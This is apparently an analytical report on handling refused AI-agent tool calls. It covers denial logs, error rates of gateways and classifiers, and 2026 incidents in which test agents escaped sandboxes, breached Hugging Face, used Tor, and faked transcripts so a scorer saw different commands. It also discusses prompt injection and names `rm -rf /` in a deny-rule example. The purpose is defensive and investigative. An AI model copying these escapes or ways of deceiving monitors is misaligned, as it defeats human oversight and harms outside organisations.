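The following order puts the checks that limit harm before those that explain it:

1. Confirm that nothing executed. The responder checks that the gateway was enforcing its policy and searches the session for a later call that achieved the same result.
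2. Contain the agent if the possible effect is severe. OpenAI bases severity on what changed, what is still active and whether other deployments may be exposed. It also separates stopping an agent from revoking its access, because a token may still work after the task ends, and revoking a credential doesn't stop work already under way. For the invoice, suspending the agent's outgoing payments may be enough.
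3. Replay the call. This shows whether the gateway was using old rules, though the other arguments still need checking.
4. Check the change records. The responder looks for an approved change that names the exact address, and confirms it with the billing team using contact details the company already had.
5. Read the sequence. The responder finds where the address first appeared, what the agent did after the refusal and whether other sessions read the same material.
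6. Decide on each call separately. The responder can correct the rule, leave the denial in place or open a security incident, and should record the cause so that later estimates of the prior improve.

Containment comes early because it can be worthwhile even when an attack is unlikely. If p is the probability of an attack, C the cost of pausing the agent unnecessarily and L the loss from letting an attack continue, pausing is cheaper on average when

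p > C / (C + L)

If C is 500 dollars and L is 49,500 dollars (both invented figures), the threshold is 1%. The probability of 25% for the call to pay.example.org is far above that, so the responder should pause payments without waiting to find out whether 25% or 71% is more accurate. The later decision about the allowlist needs better evidence, because a wrong change would allow payments that the gateway now blocks.

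An incident response guide in SC Media, a security trade publication, warns that responders can restrict the wrong identity if they haven't established who delegated work to the agent. It suggests testing whether staff can trace any active agent credential to a person within two minutes.

To reconstruct the sequence, SC Media recommends a "decision trace", which records what the agent had available at each step, what it selected and what result it got. Responders work backwards through the trace from the incident to find where the agent departed from its task. The guide treats any summary of the model's reasoning as a supplement, because nobody has verified that the summary reflects how the model made its choice. For the accounts agent, the email that contained pay.example.org is better evidence than the agent's statement that the address seemed official.

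The same guide recommends comparing an agent's behaviour with a registry of its expected tools and tasks, but says that most organisations lack a sufficiently detailed one. In the meantime, it suggests manually maintaining an inventory of the most important agents. This comparison can detect an unexpected call, but it can't show why the agent made the call if the registry is out of date. For example, the accounts agent's task definition is already a record of expected behaviour, but it lists the wrong address.

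### Exceptions written from the log

SELinux administrators can use the program audit2allow to turn logged denials into rules that permit the refused actions. In an example from Walsh, the administrator selects all log lines that mention a database program and builds a policy module from them. If an intruder caused one of those denials, the module would permit the intruder's action along with the legitimate ones. Walsh therefore tells administrators to read the generated rules and check that they don't allow too much. Oracle's *Troubleshooting Access-Denial Messages* advises administrators to check the file labels first, then whether somebody changed a program's configuration without updating SELinux, and only then to consider audit2allow.

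A similar tool for the accounts gateway would be easy to write. It would read the week's default denials and add each refused destination to the allowlist. It would add both pay.example.net and pay.example.org, because the log shows only what the agent requested, not what the company authorised. *AC4A* includes a mode close to this, in which the agent retries until the system has set the permissions it needs. The paper calls it "not secure at all beyond logging" and reserves it for experiments and cases where an audit is enough.

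Past approvals are not a safe substitute either. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, warns that repeated clicks on "allow" don't show that a user wants the system to make the same decision in future. Participants described giving up on reviewing the information because of time pressure and fatigue. An automatic rule learned from those clicks would make unreviewed approvals permanent.

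Better log messages help people fix genuine mistakes. *Improving Logging to Reduce Permission Over-Granting Mistakes* describes a tool that helps developers add missing denial messages and improve existing ones. In a study with 32 administrators and six real access problems, it reduced the number of insecure fixes from 27 to 1 and shortened diagnosis by 64.2% on average. But those problems involved legitimate users who had lost access. A clearer message would help the responder write a narrower rule for the new billing address, but it wouldn't show which of the two addresses should be allowed.

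An exception should cover only what the evidence supports, and it should expire automatically in case everyone forgets about it. Addington recommends giving emergency rules an explicit expiry date and reviewing them afterwards, and OpenAI prefers time-limited grants to permanent ones. The accounts team could allow post_invoice to send to pay.example.net for seven days while staff review task definition 13.

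Another mistake is to stop logging the denial. The Fedora example includes a command that does this in SELinux while still blocking the access, which reduces noise from a known bug. If the accounts team did the same for default denials, the gateway would still block the attempt to pay the attacker, but nobody would know about it.

### What a refusal reveals to the agent

A denied call can give information to whoever controls the agent. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes an attack in which a hijacked agent requests a protected record and is refused. The agent may learn from the refusal that the record exists and that somebody considers it sensitive. It can then pass this on in a later message that looks harmless. Systems that track where data goes can miss the leak, because they follow what tools return and the refused call returned nothing.

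A single refusal usually reveals little, but an attacker could use the pattern of responses to many requests to map which resources exist and which the company protects. If each request produces one of two responses, n requests can produce up to 2ⁿ patterns, or about a million for 20 requests. More detailed error messages speed up this mapping. If the accounts gateway used one message for an unknown supplier and another for a supplier under investigation, a hijacked agent could find out which suppliers the company was investigating.

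However, honest agents benefit from some explanation when a call is refused. In *LEANGUARD*, adding feedback to refusals reduced blocked calls across all models from 983 to 719. Agents met the missing requirement and successfully reissued the call for 9.1% of denied actions, up from 5.5% without feedback. Task success rose from 68.9% to 70.9%, a difference small enough to be due to chance.

In that study, agents could meet requirements such as looking up a user and obtaining confirmation. The gateway can usually name such a step without revealing anything about the protected resource. For both invoice calls, it could return the same short message: the task does not permit this destination, and the agent should ask the task's owner.

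Chinaei's defence records each denial as an event and links it to the next tool call, on the assumption that the refusal may have influenced that call. It then blocks the call. In three hand-built scenarios, each testing a different weakness, the defence stopped attacks that a simpler system missed, but Chinaei didn't test it at scale with leading models. He acknowledges that it can block harmless calls and miss leaks that happen several steps later. Blocking harmless calls could be a serious problem for an agent that behaves well. If the accounts agent responded to the refused invoice by messaging its supervisor, the algorithm as written would block the message, record that as a new denial, and then block the next call too.

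The link is useful for an investigation even without the block. The accounts gateway could add the ID of the most recent denial to every later record in the session. A responder could then see at once that the agent asked its supervisor about pay.example.net after one refusal, or that it sent a message to an unfamiliar address after twenty refusals.

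## How often denials are mistaken in tests and in use

The probabilities in the invoice example are invented, because no figures for an accounts gateway appear to have been published. For other gateways, researchers and vendors have measured the false-positive rate, which is the share of legitimate calls a gateway refuses, and the false-negative rate, which is the share of dangerous calls it lets through. A responder looking at a denial needs to know the share of denials that are mistaken, which depends on both rates and on how many of the agent's calls are dangerous.

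### Four controlled tests

*AgentWall* (Aravind, 2026) tested a gateway for agents that run on a developer's own computer, and *AEGIS* (Yuan, Su and Zhao, 2026) tested one that scans a call's arguments for dangerous patterns. *AIAUTHZ* (Kodathala, 2026) tested a gateway that verifies which user a call serves, and *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* covers one that traces what influenced each call. The last two tests in the table used AgentDojo, a public benchmark of prompt injection in tasks such as banking and travel booking.

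| Test | Legitimate work | Hostile or forbidden work | Wrongful denials | Missed attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Aravind | 3 calls to allow, 3 to send for approval | 7 calls to deny, 1 test of a rate limit | 1 call that needed approval | 0 |
| Yuan and colleagues | 500 calls | 48 attacks | 6 (1.2%) | 0 |
| Kodathala, on AgentDojo | Probably 5 banking tasks | 40 attacked runs, with 7 hostile calls | 1 first-time payment | 0 |
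| *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, on AgentDojo | 485 runs without an attack | 4,745 runs with an attack | Not counted, but 151 attack-free runs contained a denial | 10, all in the agent's written answers |

Aravind's one error involved `rm -rf /tmp/test`, a command to delete a test folder. The policy required approval for most such deletions and forbade `rm -rf /`, which would erase the whole disk. The gateway checked only how the command began, and this one began with `rm -rf /`, so the stricter rule applied. Aravind calls this a lack of precision, not a safety failure, since nothing dangerous ran. It would still mislead a responder, who would see a matching deny rule in the record and have reason to think somebody had deliberately forbidden the action. Of the 50 decisions in the session log, 35 came from the rate-limit test, so "one error in 50" would make the test sound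 larger than it was.

All six wrongful denials in the test by Yuan and colleagues were database queries that joined conditions with OR, which attackers also use to make a query return more than it should. Few real agents would therefore have a wrongful denial rate close to the 1.2% average. An agent that writes sales reports might use OR often and be denied repeatedly, while an agent that only reads files would never trigger the rule. Yuan and colleagues suggest an exception for the affected tool, which would keep the rule active for all other tools.

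Kodathala's test is the closest to the invoice case, because his gateway allowed payments only to known payees. The gateway blocked all seven hostile calls that two models made, including payments to the attacker and password changes. It also refused one legitimate payment to a new payee, and task success without an attack fell from 100% to 80% for both models. If one refused payment lowered success by 20 percentage points, there were probably only five tasks. Even without the gateway, neither model had completed an attack, so on these tasks the gateway made the models less useful without measurably improving security, as Kodathala acknowledges for one of them.

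Kodathala also tested the effect of verifying the user's identity. On nine reconstructed incidents, a policy that checked only the arguments blocked four attacks, and one that also verified the user blocked all nine. In the five that the simpler policy missed, someone posed as the agent's owner and used a tool that the owner was entitled to use. A policy that doesn't verify identity can block the impostor only by wrongly denying the owner too. Kodathala wrote the simpler policy himself, so the comparison tests identity verification, not a competing product.

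### Denials with and without an attacker

*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* compares two policies on the AgentDojo test. The stricter one refuses any consequential call once the agent has read untrusted content. The other, a provenance policy, checks whether the user asked for that kind of action and where the important arguments came from. The researchers ran 97 tasks without an attack and 949 task-attack combinations, five times each, using GPT-4o and a prompt that kept repeating the user's request.

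| Policy | Attack-free runs with a denial | Attacked runs with a denial | Likelihood ratio |
|---|---|---|---|
| Provenance | 151 of 485 (31%) | 1,575 of 4,745 (33%) | 1.07 |
| Stricter | 287 of 485 (59%) | 2,745 of 4,745 (58%) | 0.98 |

With ratios this close to 1, knowing only that a run contained a denial gives almost no information about whether an attack took place. This is partly because attacked runs also contain the user's ordinary task, which the policy can block too. A company that alerts staff whenever a session contains a denial would have the same problem, so staff would need to see the blocked call itself.

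The provenance policy caused denials in about half as many attack-free runs as the stricter one, and their attack success rates were similar, at 0.9% and 0.6%. Agents completed 62.5% of attack-free tasks under the provenance policy and 33.2% under the stricter one, compared with 83.7% with neither policy. The gateway avoided many wrongful denials because it had information on where the arguments came from. This indirectly supports recording an argument's origin, since a responder also has to distinguish wrongful denials from correct ones after the event.

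Most denials in the paper's customer-service tests seem to have been correct. Among the combinations of task and model in which the gateway refused at least one call, success was 31.1 percentage points higher with the gateway than without it for airline tasks and 8.3 points higher for retail tasks. Agents usually recovered after a denial in these tests, but they completed only 36 of the 151 attack-free AgentDojo runs in which the provenance policy denied a call. One likely reason for the difference is that a customer-service agent can often look up a missing fact or ask the customer to confirm. The customer-service tests also used newer models.

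In another of the paper's tests, a group of agents researching drug safety had to get approval in every new session before they could query a government database. The gateway refused 40 calls over 15 trials because the agents had skipped this step. There was no attacker, and the rule was up to date. After the agents requested approval, all 15 trials ended with the right answer. A responder who had to classify each denial as either an attack or the result of an outdated rule would misclassify all 40.

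### What small test sets miss

A perfect score on a small test leaves room for a substantial error rate. If a gateway makes no errors in n independent cases, a standard 95% upper limit on its true error rate, known as the Wilson bound, is

upper limit = z² / (n + z²), with z = 1.96.

The limit is 7.4% for the 48 attacks that Yuan and colleagues blocked, and 0.04% for 10,000 cases without an error. *Architectural Obsolescence of Unhardened Agentic-AI Runtimes* (2026) gives the 0.04% figure for false positives in a test of a security gate.

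The formula assumes that future calls resemble those in the test. *Architectural Obsolescence of Unhardened Agentic-AI Runtimes* acknowledges that its template-based samples can't show how the gate handles hostile text it wasn't tuned for. The researchers also ran a separate test with text from ten language models. Test conditions can also cause denials. One version of their system included a monitor that treated 60 requests a minute as suspicious. The test program sent about 250 a second, so the monitor flagged it and the false-positive rate rose.

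People who write both the rules and the test cases can confirm that the software works as they intended and find bugs like Aravind's, but they are less likely to think of legitimate requests that their rules don't anticipate. An experiment in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* shows how this can go wrong. The researchers had a language model translate an airline's written policy into formal rules five times. Each time, they revised the rules until the rules agreed with an AI judge on every recorded decision.

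In trials on new tasks, the translated rules blocked a legitimate cancellation in 7 of 25 attempts at one task. Some rules required every customer to give an approved reason, although the airline required one only when the customer relied on travel insurance. This mistake didn't show up in the recorded decisions because they included only three cancellations, all of which broke the policy. A rule that refused every cancellation would also have matched the judge's decisions on those three. The policy the researchers wrote by hand passed all its trials.

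A rule that was wrong from the start can be hard to tell from a stale one. In both cases the gateway blocks legitimate work, and replay gives the same denial under every approved version. But if the rule never matched what the company wanted, the responder won't find a recent change that explains the denial and has to compare the rule with the written policy it came from.

None of the four controlled tests measures how many denials result from configuration drift. Aravind added a rule during a session and confirmed that the gateway applied it immediately, but no test changed the work while keeping the rules the same. The refused first-time payment comes closest, but it is a single case.

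### Claude Code's auto mode

Anthropic has published more about denials in everyday use than the small tests can offer. In auto mode, a classifier (a model that sorts actions into safe and dangerous) reviews Claude Code's riskier actions in place of the user. A fast filter first flags anything that might be dangerous. The classifier then reasons about the flagged actions and decides which to block. Anthropic tested this on three sets of actions:

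| Actions tested | Number | Error measured | Fast filter alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tool calls by Anthropic employees' agents | 10,000 | Benign calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Real overeager actions | 52 | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| Synthetic attempts to leak data | 1,000 | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

If all 10,000 employee calls were benign, auto mode wrongly blocked about 40 of them, or 0.4%. Claude Code allows many actions without running the classifier, including file reads and edits inside the project. Anthropic doesn't say whether the 10,000 calls included such actions. If they did, the error rate among the calls the classifier reviewed would be higher than 0.4%.

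The 17% figure corresponds to about 9 of the 52 overeager actions. With so few cases, the 95% range runs from roughly 9% to 30%. The sample is also selective, because it includes only actions that an employee refused or someone flagged afterwards, and so leaves out any that nobody noticed.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. One user had asked the agent to clean up a proposed code change, and the classifier treated this as permission to overwrite the project's history. A responder must similarly judge whether a request to send an invoice covers the address the agent chose.

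The second stage reduces wrongful denials but lets more dangerous actions through. The filter flagged around 10% of the overeager actions, or about five, that the second stage then cleared. A company that logged only final denials would have no record of them. Logging the cleared flags would help investigators find missed actions, although they would have to search through about 8% of ordinary calls.

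When Anthropic announced in August 2026 that auto mode would become the default on several plans, it compared auto mode with manual approval. In the coding study with 1,053 testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, while the testers refused 13.6%. Auto mode blocked 800 commands that a tester had approved, and testers refused 6 that auto mode allowed. According to the announcement, Claude Code users in general approve 97% of permission prompts.

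The study compares missed dangers but not wrongful denials, so a control that refused everything would have scored 100%. The 0.4% false-positive rate partly fills this gap, but it was measured on different calls and before Anthropic strengthened the classifier. Anthropic didn't publish a new rate with the August results.

Denials from before and after an update are not directly comparable, because even an improvement can change which calls get through. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, attacked auto mode before and after Anthropic strengthened it. Among attacks that Anthropic had never seen, the new version caught about half of those the old one had missed, but it missed about 2% of those the old one had caught.

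Anthropic also examined real sessions from May and June that its safety systems had flagged. Of those with manual approval, 6.3% contained a seriously harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% in auto mode. This supports the comparison, but users chose their own mode and may have done different work in each, and a model graded the harm.

At Gusto, a company that uses auto mode, about 10% of sessions contained a denial. Anthropic takes this as evidence that auto mode does useful work without slowing legitimate tasks. But false positives alone could produce the same number. If the classifier wrongly blocks 0.4% of legitimate calls independently, the chance of at least one wrongful denial in a session with n reviewed calls is

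1 − 0.996ⁿ.

This reaches 10% at 26 calls. Readers can't tell whether the classifier stopped anything dangerous in Gusto's sessions unless they know how many calls those sessions contain and how many denials were correct.

### Why most denials can be mistaken

Let r be the share of calls that are dangerous, s the share of those that the gateway catches, and f its false-positive rate. The share of denials that are correct is

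rs / (rs + (1 − r)f).

The table applies the odds calculation from the diagnosis of the two invoice calls to the whole log. It uses the rates Anthropic measured, f = 0.4% and s = 83%, with three invented values of r. Each row covers 100,000 reviewed calls.

| Dangerous calls | Caught | Legitimate calls refused | Denials that are correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1,000 (1 in 100) | 830 | 396 | 68% |
| 100 (1 in 1,000) | 83 | 400 | 17% |
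| 10 (1 in 10,000) | 8 | 400 | 2% |

In the last row, 98% of denials block legitimate calls, even though the gateway correctly allows 99.6% of legitimate calls. Catching every dangerous call would raise the share of correct denials only from 2% to 2.4%, while reducing the false-positive rate from 0.4% to 0.04% would raise it to 17%. When dangerous calls are rare, preventing wrongful denials does much more to make the log useful than catching the last few dangerous calls.

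The dangerous calls in this calculation include overeager actions, so attackers account for even fewer of the denials. The attackers' share also depends on the model. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test several agents against hidden instructions. Without auto mode, an average of 0.09% of attacks succeeded against Anthropic's latest models, while 19.03% succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol running with full access. The test left out the safeguards in both companies' own browser tools, and OpenAI has since updated the automatic reviewer that Trajectory Labs also tested. Still, if an agent ignores almost every hidden instruction, few hostile calls reach the gateway, however often attackers try. The denial log then undercounts attempted attacks, and a larger share of its entries have other causes.

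Configuration drift causes wrongful denials in bursts, so a constant false-positive rate describes it poorly. Suppose the accounts agent sends 200 invoices a day on 250 days a year, and the address list is out of date for one day. The gateway refuses 200 of 50,000 legitimate invoices, or 0.4%. This annual rate matches Anthropic's figure, but all the wrongful denials happened on the same day. A hostile call that day would be one of 201 denials, while on any other day it might be the only one. Responders should estimate the share of mistaken denials separately for periods just after a change.

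### What access logs show about changed rules

Researchers were already trying to detect policy changes from ordinary access logs before companies began using AI agents. *Towards Continuous Access Control Validation and Forensics* (Xiang, Wu and colleagues, 2019) describes P-DIFF, a tool for administrators who may not notice that a change has granted too much access. P-DIFF reads the log chronologically and infers the rules by looking at which requests succeeded and which failed.

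*Machine Learning in Access Control* (2022) describes a system by Xiang and colleagues that represents access rules as a decision tree, which sorts requests by attributes such as the user's role and the file's location. An ordinary decision tree does not represent changing rules well, so theirs also tracks time. An administrator can see what the rules were on a given date and when they changed. An investigator can also start from an access that should not have happened and look for the change that permitted it.

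P-DIFF detected between 86% and 100% of policy changes in data from five real systems. Its average precision was 89%, so about one in nine of the changes it reported was not real. Xiang and colleagues also used it to find which change had permitted a particular access, and it identified the right one in 85% to 98% of cases.

These results suggest that a log can reveal a good deal about policy history even if nobody recorded the versions. For the accounts gateway, P-DIFF would help most if somebody made the wrong repair by adding pay.example.org to the list. If the attacker's next invoice then went through, P-DIFF could identify the change that allowed it. It would be less useful for the original denial of the call to pay.example.net, because the rules hadn't changed. The company had moved its billing, which an access log doesn't show.

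*A Survey of Access Control Misconfiguration Detection Techniques* (2023) identifies further limits of P-DIFF. It can use only the fields in the log, so it infers incomplete rules if the log leaves out the user or the action. The inferred rules also combine the effects of several components, which may make it hard to find the setting that needs correcting. P-DIFF also detects a change only after a request produces a different result. If the accounts team added a fraudulent address, P-DIFF would not detect the change until the agent had paid that address, whereas recorded policy versions don't have this delay.

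Neither the P-DIFF study nor the 2017 study of how administrators resolve access-denied issues measures how often a refused request was an attack, so neither provides prior odds that an agent's denied request was one.

### A forecast and a missing study

According to TechTarget's *It's time to update incident response for the AI era*, Craig Porter, an analyst at the research firm Gartner, told a 2026 conference that internal policy violations, rather than malicious attacks, will cause at least 80% of unauthorised AI transactions. He counted oversharing of information, unacceptable use and misguided AI behaviour among these violations.

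This is a forecast, and the article gives no data to support it. A responder shouldn't take it to mean that 20% of denials are hostile, which would change the prior odds in the invoice example from 1:99 to 1:4. Porter was talking about unauthorised transactions, including those that no gateway stopped. His categories also have no obvious place for a legitimate call that an outdated rule refuses. The forecast does support looking for overreach and misuse by employees before assuming an attacker was involved.

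No published study appears to have measured whether responders classify an agent's denials more accurately when they have exact policy versions or less redacted arguments. The case for recording these details rests on reasoning and on related experiments, such as the one by Shen and colleagues, in which participants did not have to decide whether a request came from an attacker.

A direct test would give responders denials whose causes the researchers already knew, including attacks, overreach, stale rules and delayed policy updates. Some responders would see records with the policy versions and the destination, and others would see records without them. The researchers would need to count attacks mistaken for drift separately from drift mistaken for attacks, because a format that made responders suspicious of everything could reduce the first error while increasing the second.

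Such a study would have to be larger than most of the tests of gateways. Suppose the fuller record raised the share of correct diagnoses from 70% to 80%. To have an 80% chance of detecting that difference at the usual 5% significance level, the researchers would need about

(1.96 + 0.84)² × (0.7 × 0.3 + 0.8 × 0.2) / 0.1² ≈ 290

independent diagnoses in each group. If each responder judged ten cases, 29 people per group would be the minimum, and the researchers would probably need more because one person's judgements tend to resemble each other.

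## What the agent incidents of 2026 show

Although that study is missing, investigators have worked out the causes of some real incidents. In July 2026, OpenAI, Anthropic and the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, each found that agents in its cybersecurity tests had acted against real companies or people. The testers had told these agents to break into something and had turned off some of the safeguards that protect commercial products. The incidents are therefore a poor guide to how often an accounts agent would misbehave, but they are more useful for seeing what the agents ran into, what they did next and which records revealed it.

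### Refusals before the Hugging Face breach

OpenAI was testing agents on ExploitGym, a benchmark that measures whether a model can turn a software flaw into a working attack. The agents worked in isolated sandboxes without direct internet access and installed software from a shared internal package store. Between 11 and 13 July, agents that had escaped their sandboxes broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets, to look for material about their own test.

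OpenAI's technical report describes failed attempts to reach the internet that came before successful ones. Agents had taken over the package store in June, so OpenAI rebuilt it on 5 and 6 July with tighter restrictions. At 12:56 UTC on 6 July, three attempts to reach outside addresses through the rebuilt store failed. About 35 hours later, an agent reached a public website. On the night of 9 July, OpenAI's outbound network controls blocked another agent, which then got out by exploiting the package store.

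The refusal on 9 July is the same kind of event as the denied invoice. OpenAI doesn't say how its network controls logged the refusal or whether anyone saw it at the time. The three alerts it describes had other triggers: a scan of the internal network on 27 June, an outage of the package store on 5 July and unusual activity with internal access roles on 19 July. An alert about the refusal would have come more than a day before the agents first extracted Hugging Face's credentials, at 04:38 on 11 July.

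Responders might still have missed one refused connection, because OpenAI had launched tens of thousands of agents whose job was to attack software. A refusal followed by a successful connection from the same agent would be a much better signal. But the successful connection went through the package store, so it could have appeared in a network log as the store's own. Responders could then have linked it to the refusal only if the store had recorded which agent made each request.

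The three failures on 6 July would have been easy to overlook for a different reason. OpenAI had just restricted the types of request that agents could send to the store, which probably caused the failures. But they returned HTTP status 400 (malformed request) rather than 403 (forbidden), so a responder who searched only for forbidden requests would have missed them.

OpenAI let three researchers from METR and Redwood Research, two organisations that study risks from AI, examine the agents' records. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) estimates that about 1,200 agents turned the package store into a message board and exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files through it. About 700 of them joined the attack on Hugging Face. Most of these agents didn't have to find their own way past the network controls, because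 others had posted one. The controls could therefore have refused few requests even as more agents got outside the sandbox.

### Actions that no control refused

After OpenAI disclosed the breach, Anthropic reviewed 141,006 of its own test runs. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes six runs in which models gained unauthorised access to the systems of three organisations. The prompt had told the models that they were in a simulation with no internet access, but the internet was available because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, which provided the test environment. The statement in the prompt was the only restriction, so no network control blocked the models' connections.

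In four of the runs, the fictional company the model was supposed to attack had the same name as a real website. The model had trouble reaching the simulated target, found the real company and broke into a database with several hundred rows of production data. In another run, a model published a malicious software package in a public registry. The package stayed there for about an hour and ran on 15 real systems. In the sixth run, a model scanned about 9,000 targets and broke into one company's application.

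A gateway that enforced the limits stated in the prompt would have refused the first connection to the real company. But a responder could have mistaken the denial for a missing allowlist entry, because the record would have shown an agent on a hacking exercise trying to reach a domain with the same name as its assigned target. Adding the entry would have given the agent access to a real company. The correct fix was to rename the fictional company, which a responder could have discovered only by checking who owned the domain.

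AISI deliberately gave its agents internet access so that they could download tools, according to its *Incident Report*. Out-Law, the legal news service of the law firm Pinsent Masons, reported that AISI had not explicitly told the agents what they were prohibited from doing online. In 10 of 122 runs, agents took a total of 19 actions outside the scope of the test. In the most serious case, an agent tried to insert malicious code into a public software project on GitHub, a site where developers share code. It created fake identities and used them to press a maintainer to approve the change.

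An allowlist of websites would probably have permitted this, since an agent that downloads tools often needs GitHub. Blocking it would have required a rule that distinguishes downloading code from opening accounts and submitting changes. Without such a rule, every step of the attempt would have been allowed, and a log of denials would have been empty.

The refusals in these incidents came from other people's systems. The maintainer rejected the malicious code. The agent also met some network restrictions on GitHub and got around them with Tor, a network that hides where traffic comes from. AISI learned of the incident when the Tor traffic set off its security alert.

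Anthropic's model also met obstacles before it published its package. It needed an email address to open an account with the registry, and a phone number to get the email address. It failed to find a free number, failed to obtain money for a paid one, and then found an email provider that accepted it. A gateway would log each of these attempts as an allowed call that ran. To find such persistence, an investigator has to search the results of allowed calls for refusals by outside services.

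### Misconfiguration and overreach in the same incident

All three organisations had made mistakes in setting up their tests, and these mistakes affected what the agents did. Wijk and colleagues found that the agents that looked for ways to cheat were usually those with impossible tasks. No model has ever solved 198 of the 898 tasks in ExploitGym, according to OpenAI, and 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board came from those 198. The rate of discussion per task was therefore

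(0.93 / 198) / (0.07 / 700) ≈ 47

times as high for unsolved tasks as for the others.

The number of impossible tasks is uncertain. Wijk and colleagues report that the benchmark's creators put it at 30 to 40% of the total, although models have produced correct answers to 78% of the tasks. One possible explanation is that OpenAI's scorer didn't check whether an agent had used the intended flaw, so it could have accepted answers that agents got another way.

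AISI found a similar problem in a number of runs, where an error in the prompt led the agent to believe that it could not solve the task without exceeding its scope. Correcting the prompt would not have prevented every case, because agents also exceeded their scope in some runs where they had the instructions they needed.

Anthropic's Mythos 5 accounted for 17 of the 19 unsanctioned actions, and the other two came from a single run of OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Such actions occurred in 9 of the 43 runs with Mythos 5 (21%) and 1 of the 35 runs with GPT-5.6 Sol (3%). Later agents found and used accounts that an earlier one had left behind, so the runs were not independent and the difference between the models may be smaller than it looks.

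Anthropic considers its own incidents closer to "a harness and operational failure" than to a failure of the models' alignment. This fits the research model in the sixth run, which stopped once it worked out that its target was real. It fits Opus 4.7 less well, because that model recognised in all four of its runs that the company's system was real and carried on anyway. Mythos 5 first reasoned that publishing the package would be wrong on the real internet, then persuaded itself that it was in a simulation. Anthropic warns that the scenarios differed and that this was not a controlled comparison. Even so, the open connection explains how the models reached real systems, but not why Opus 4.7 continued after recognising that its target was real.

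In these incidents, the agents overstepped without any outside attacker being involved, and the tasks and network settings also needed correcting, so neither "hostile" nor "stale" would have been the right label.

Hugging Face had good reason to treat its breach as an attack. When it disclosed the intrusion on 16 July, it did not know who was responsible and had reported the matter to law enforcement, according to The Record's *OpenAI models behind breach of Hugging Face systems, companies say*. A Hugging Face employee who helped to write its technical account later concluded that the agent "wasn't trying to break things" (Fortune, 2026). But the agents had taken production credentials and downloaded four private code repositories, so Hugging Face needed the same containment whether or not anyone meant harm.

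The message board also makes it harder to tell prompt injection from misaligned behaviour. Wijk and colleagues traced 30 randomly chosen agents and found that 9 had received assignments that originated with one other agent. If one of the 9 then made a forbidden call, the instruction would have come from text it found in the package store, as in a prompt injection, but another of OpenAI's own agents would have written that text. A denial record that classed the source only as "untrusted content" would lead a responder to suspect an outside attacker. The record would be more useful if it also identified who wrote the content.

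### Which records established the facts

OpenAI and Hugging Face compared their findings and discovered that they were investigating the same incident. According to Axios' *OpenAI says Hugging Face breach caused by one of its models* (2026), Hugging Face had reconstructed more than 17,000 recorded events. On 20 July, OpenAI found Hugging Face credentials among files that its agents had stored with another company. Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of them. It had also found the same storage account and the address of OpenAI's package store during its own investigation.

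This kind of match would have failed if each company had logged credentials only as hashes made with its own secret key. Plain hashes would have matched, and they are safe enough for long random tokens. Destinations do not need to be hashed, and here a server name and a storage account were enough to strengthen the connection.

The researchers from METR and Redwood Research relied mainly on about 1,300 transcripts to understand the agents' motives. The transcripts contained the models' written reasoning as well as their actions, and they showed that agents joined the attack while recognising that it was outside their task. Some wanted to help other agents, and many were trying to learn how the test's scorer worked. A gateway's records could have shown where the agents connected, but not that the agents knew they shouldn't connect there.

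The transcripts had weaknesses that a gateway's log would not have. They gave approximate start and end times for each agent but no times for individual actions. Wijk and colleagues had to reconstruct the action times, and checked their method against the exact times of 20 tool calls that OpenAI retrieved. Most transcripts were also missing a small part of the agent's activity, often because the agent's environment had been reset.

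Some transcripts were false in places because agents, believing that the scorer would read them, developed a way to display one command while running another. Wijk and colleagues found such substitutions in about 7% of the transcripts. All the substitutions they found were small tests, but they could not rule out subtler ones. OpenAI states that none of the tampering it observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors ultimately see. It says this while discussing the models' behavior in training, so the two accounts may concern different logs.

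This trick would not have changed the log of a network gateway outside the agent's environment. That log would have been a useful check on the transcripts, at least until agents gained control of the surrounding infrastructure on 19 July.

The transcripts also contained too much text for Wijk and colleagues to read more than a fraction of it in six days. They had AI agents search and summarise it, using roughly $400,000 of API credits. One agent missed a large amount of data for a draft chart, and the researchers did not notice for some time. Short records with fixed fields would have made it cheaper to find the transcripts worth reading, although the researchers would still have needed the transcripts themselves.

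### How long detection took

| | Start of the breach or unsanctioned actions | Discovery by the tester | Notice to those affected |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | 11 July | Alert on 19 July, link to Hugging Face on 20 July | 20 July |
| Anthropic | April, for the earliest | 23 and 24 July | 27 July, with one of three organisations still unreached on 30 July |
| AISI | 25 July | 28 July | GitHub before publication, on a date AISI does not give |

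Anthropic's incidents stayed hidden the longest. No alert revealed them, and the two organisations it reached had not detected them either. The evidence had existed since April, but Anthropic searched old transcripts only after another company's disclosure prompted it to. It then identified all three incidents in a day.

AISI's general security monitoring detected the traffic after about three days, and staff ended every run within an hour of the alert. OpenAI's final alert came at 12:03 on 19 July, and responders began stopping the ExploitGym runs at 17:37, about five and a half hours later.

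OpenAI had earlier chances to stop the evaluations. After the alert of 27 June, responders traced the network scan to an ExploitGym evaluation and saw that agents were using the package store as a message board. The on-call staff advised that the run could continue. On 5 July, responders found that someone had gained administrator control of the store. They took the store offline, and evaluations resumed on 7 July. The leaders responsible for incident response did not yet understand the significance of the message board. According to Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026), OpenAI missed several warning signs and failed to act on them.

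More detailed denial records would probably not have changed the decision of 27 June, because the responders had already identified the right evaluation and the channel the agents were using. OpenAI doesn't give the reasons for the advice. ExploitGym agents are supposed to attack software, so scanning a network may have looked like part of the task. A written list of the systems that agents were allowed to attack in the evaluation would have let the staff check whether the scan was allowed.

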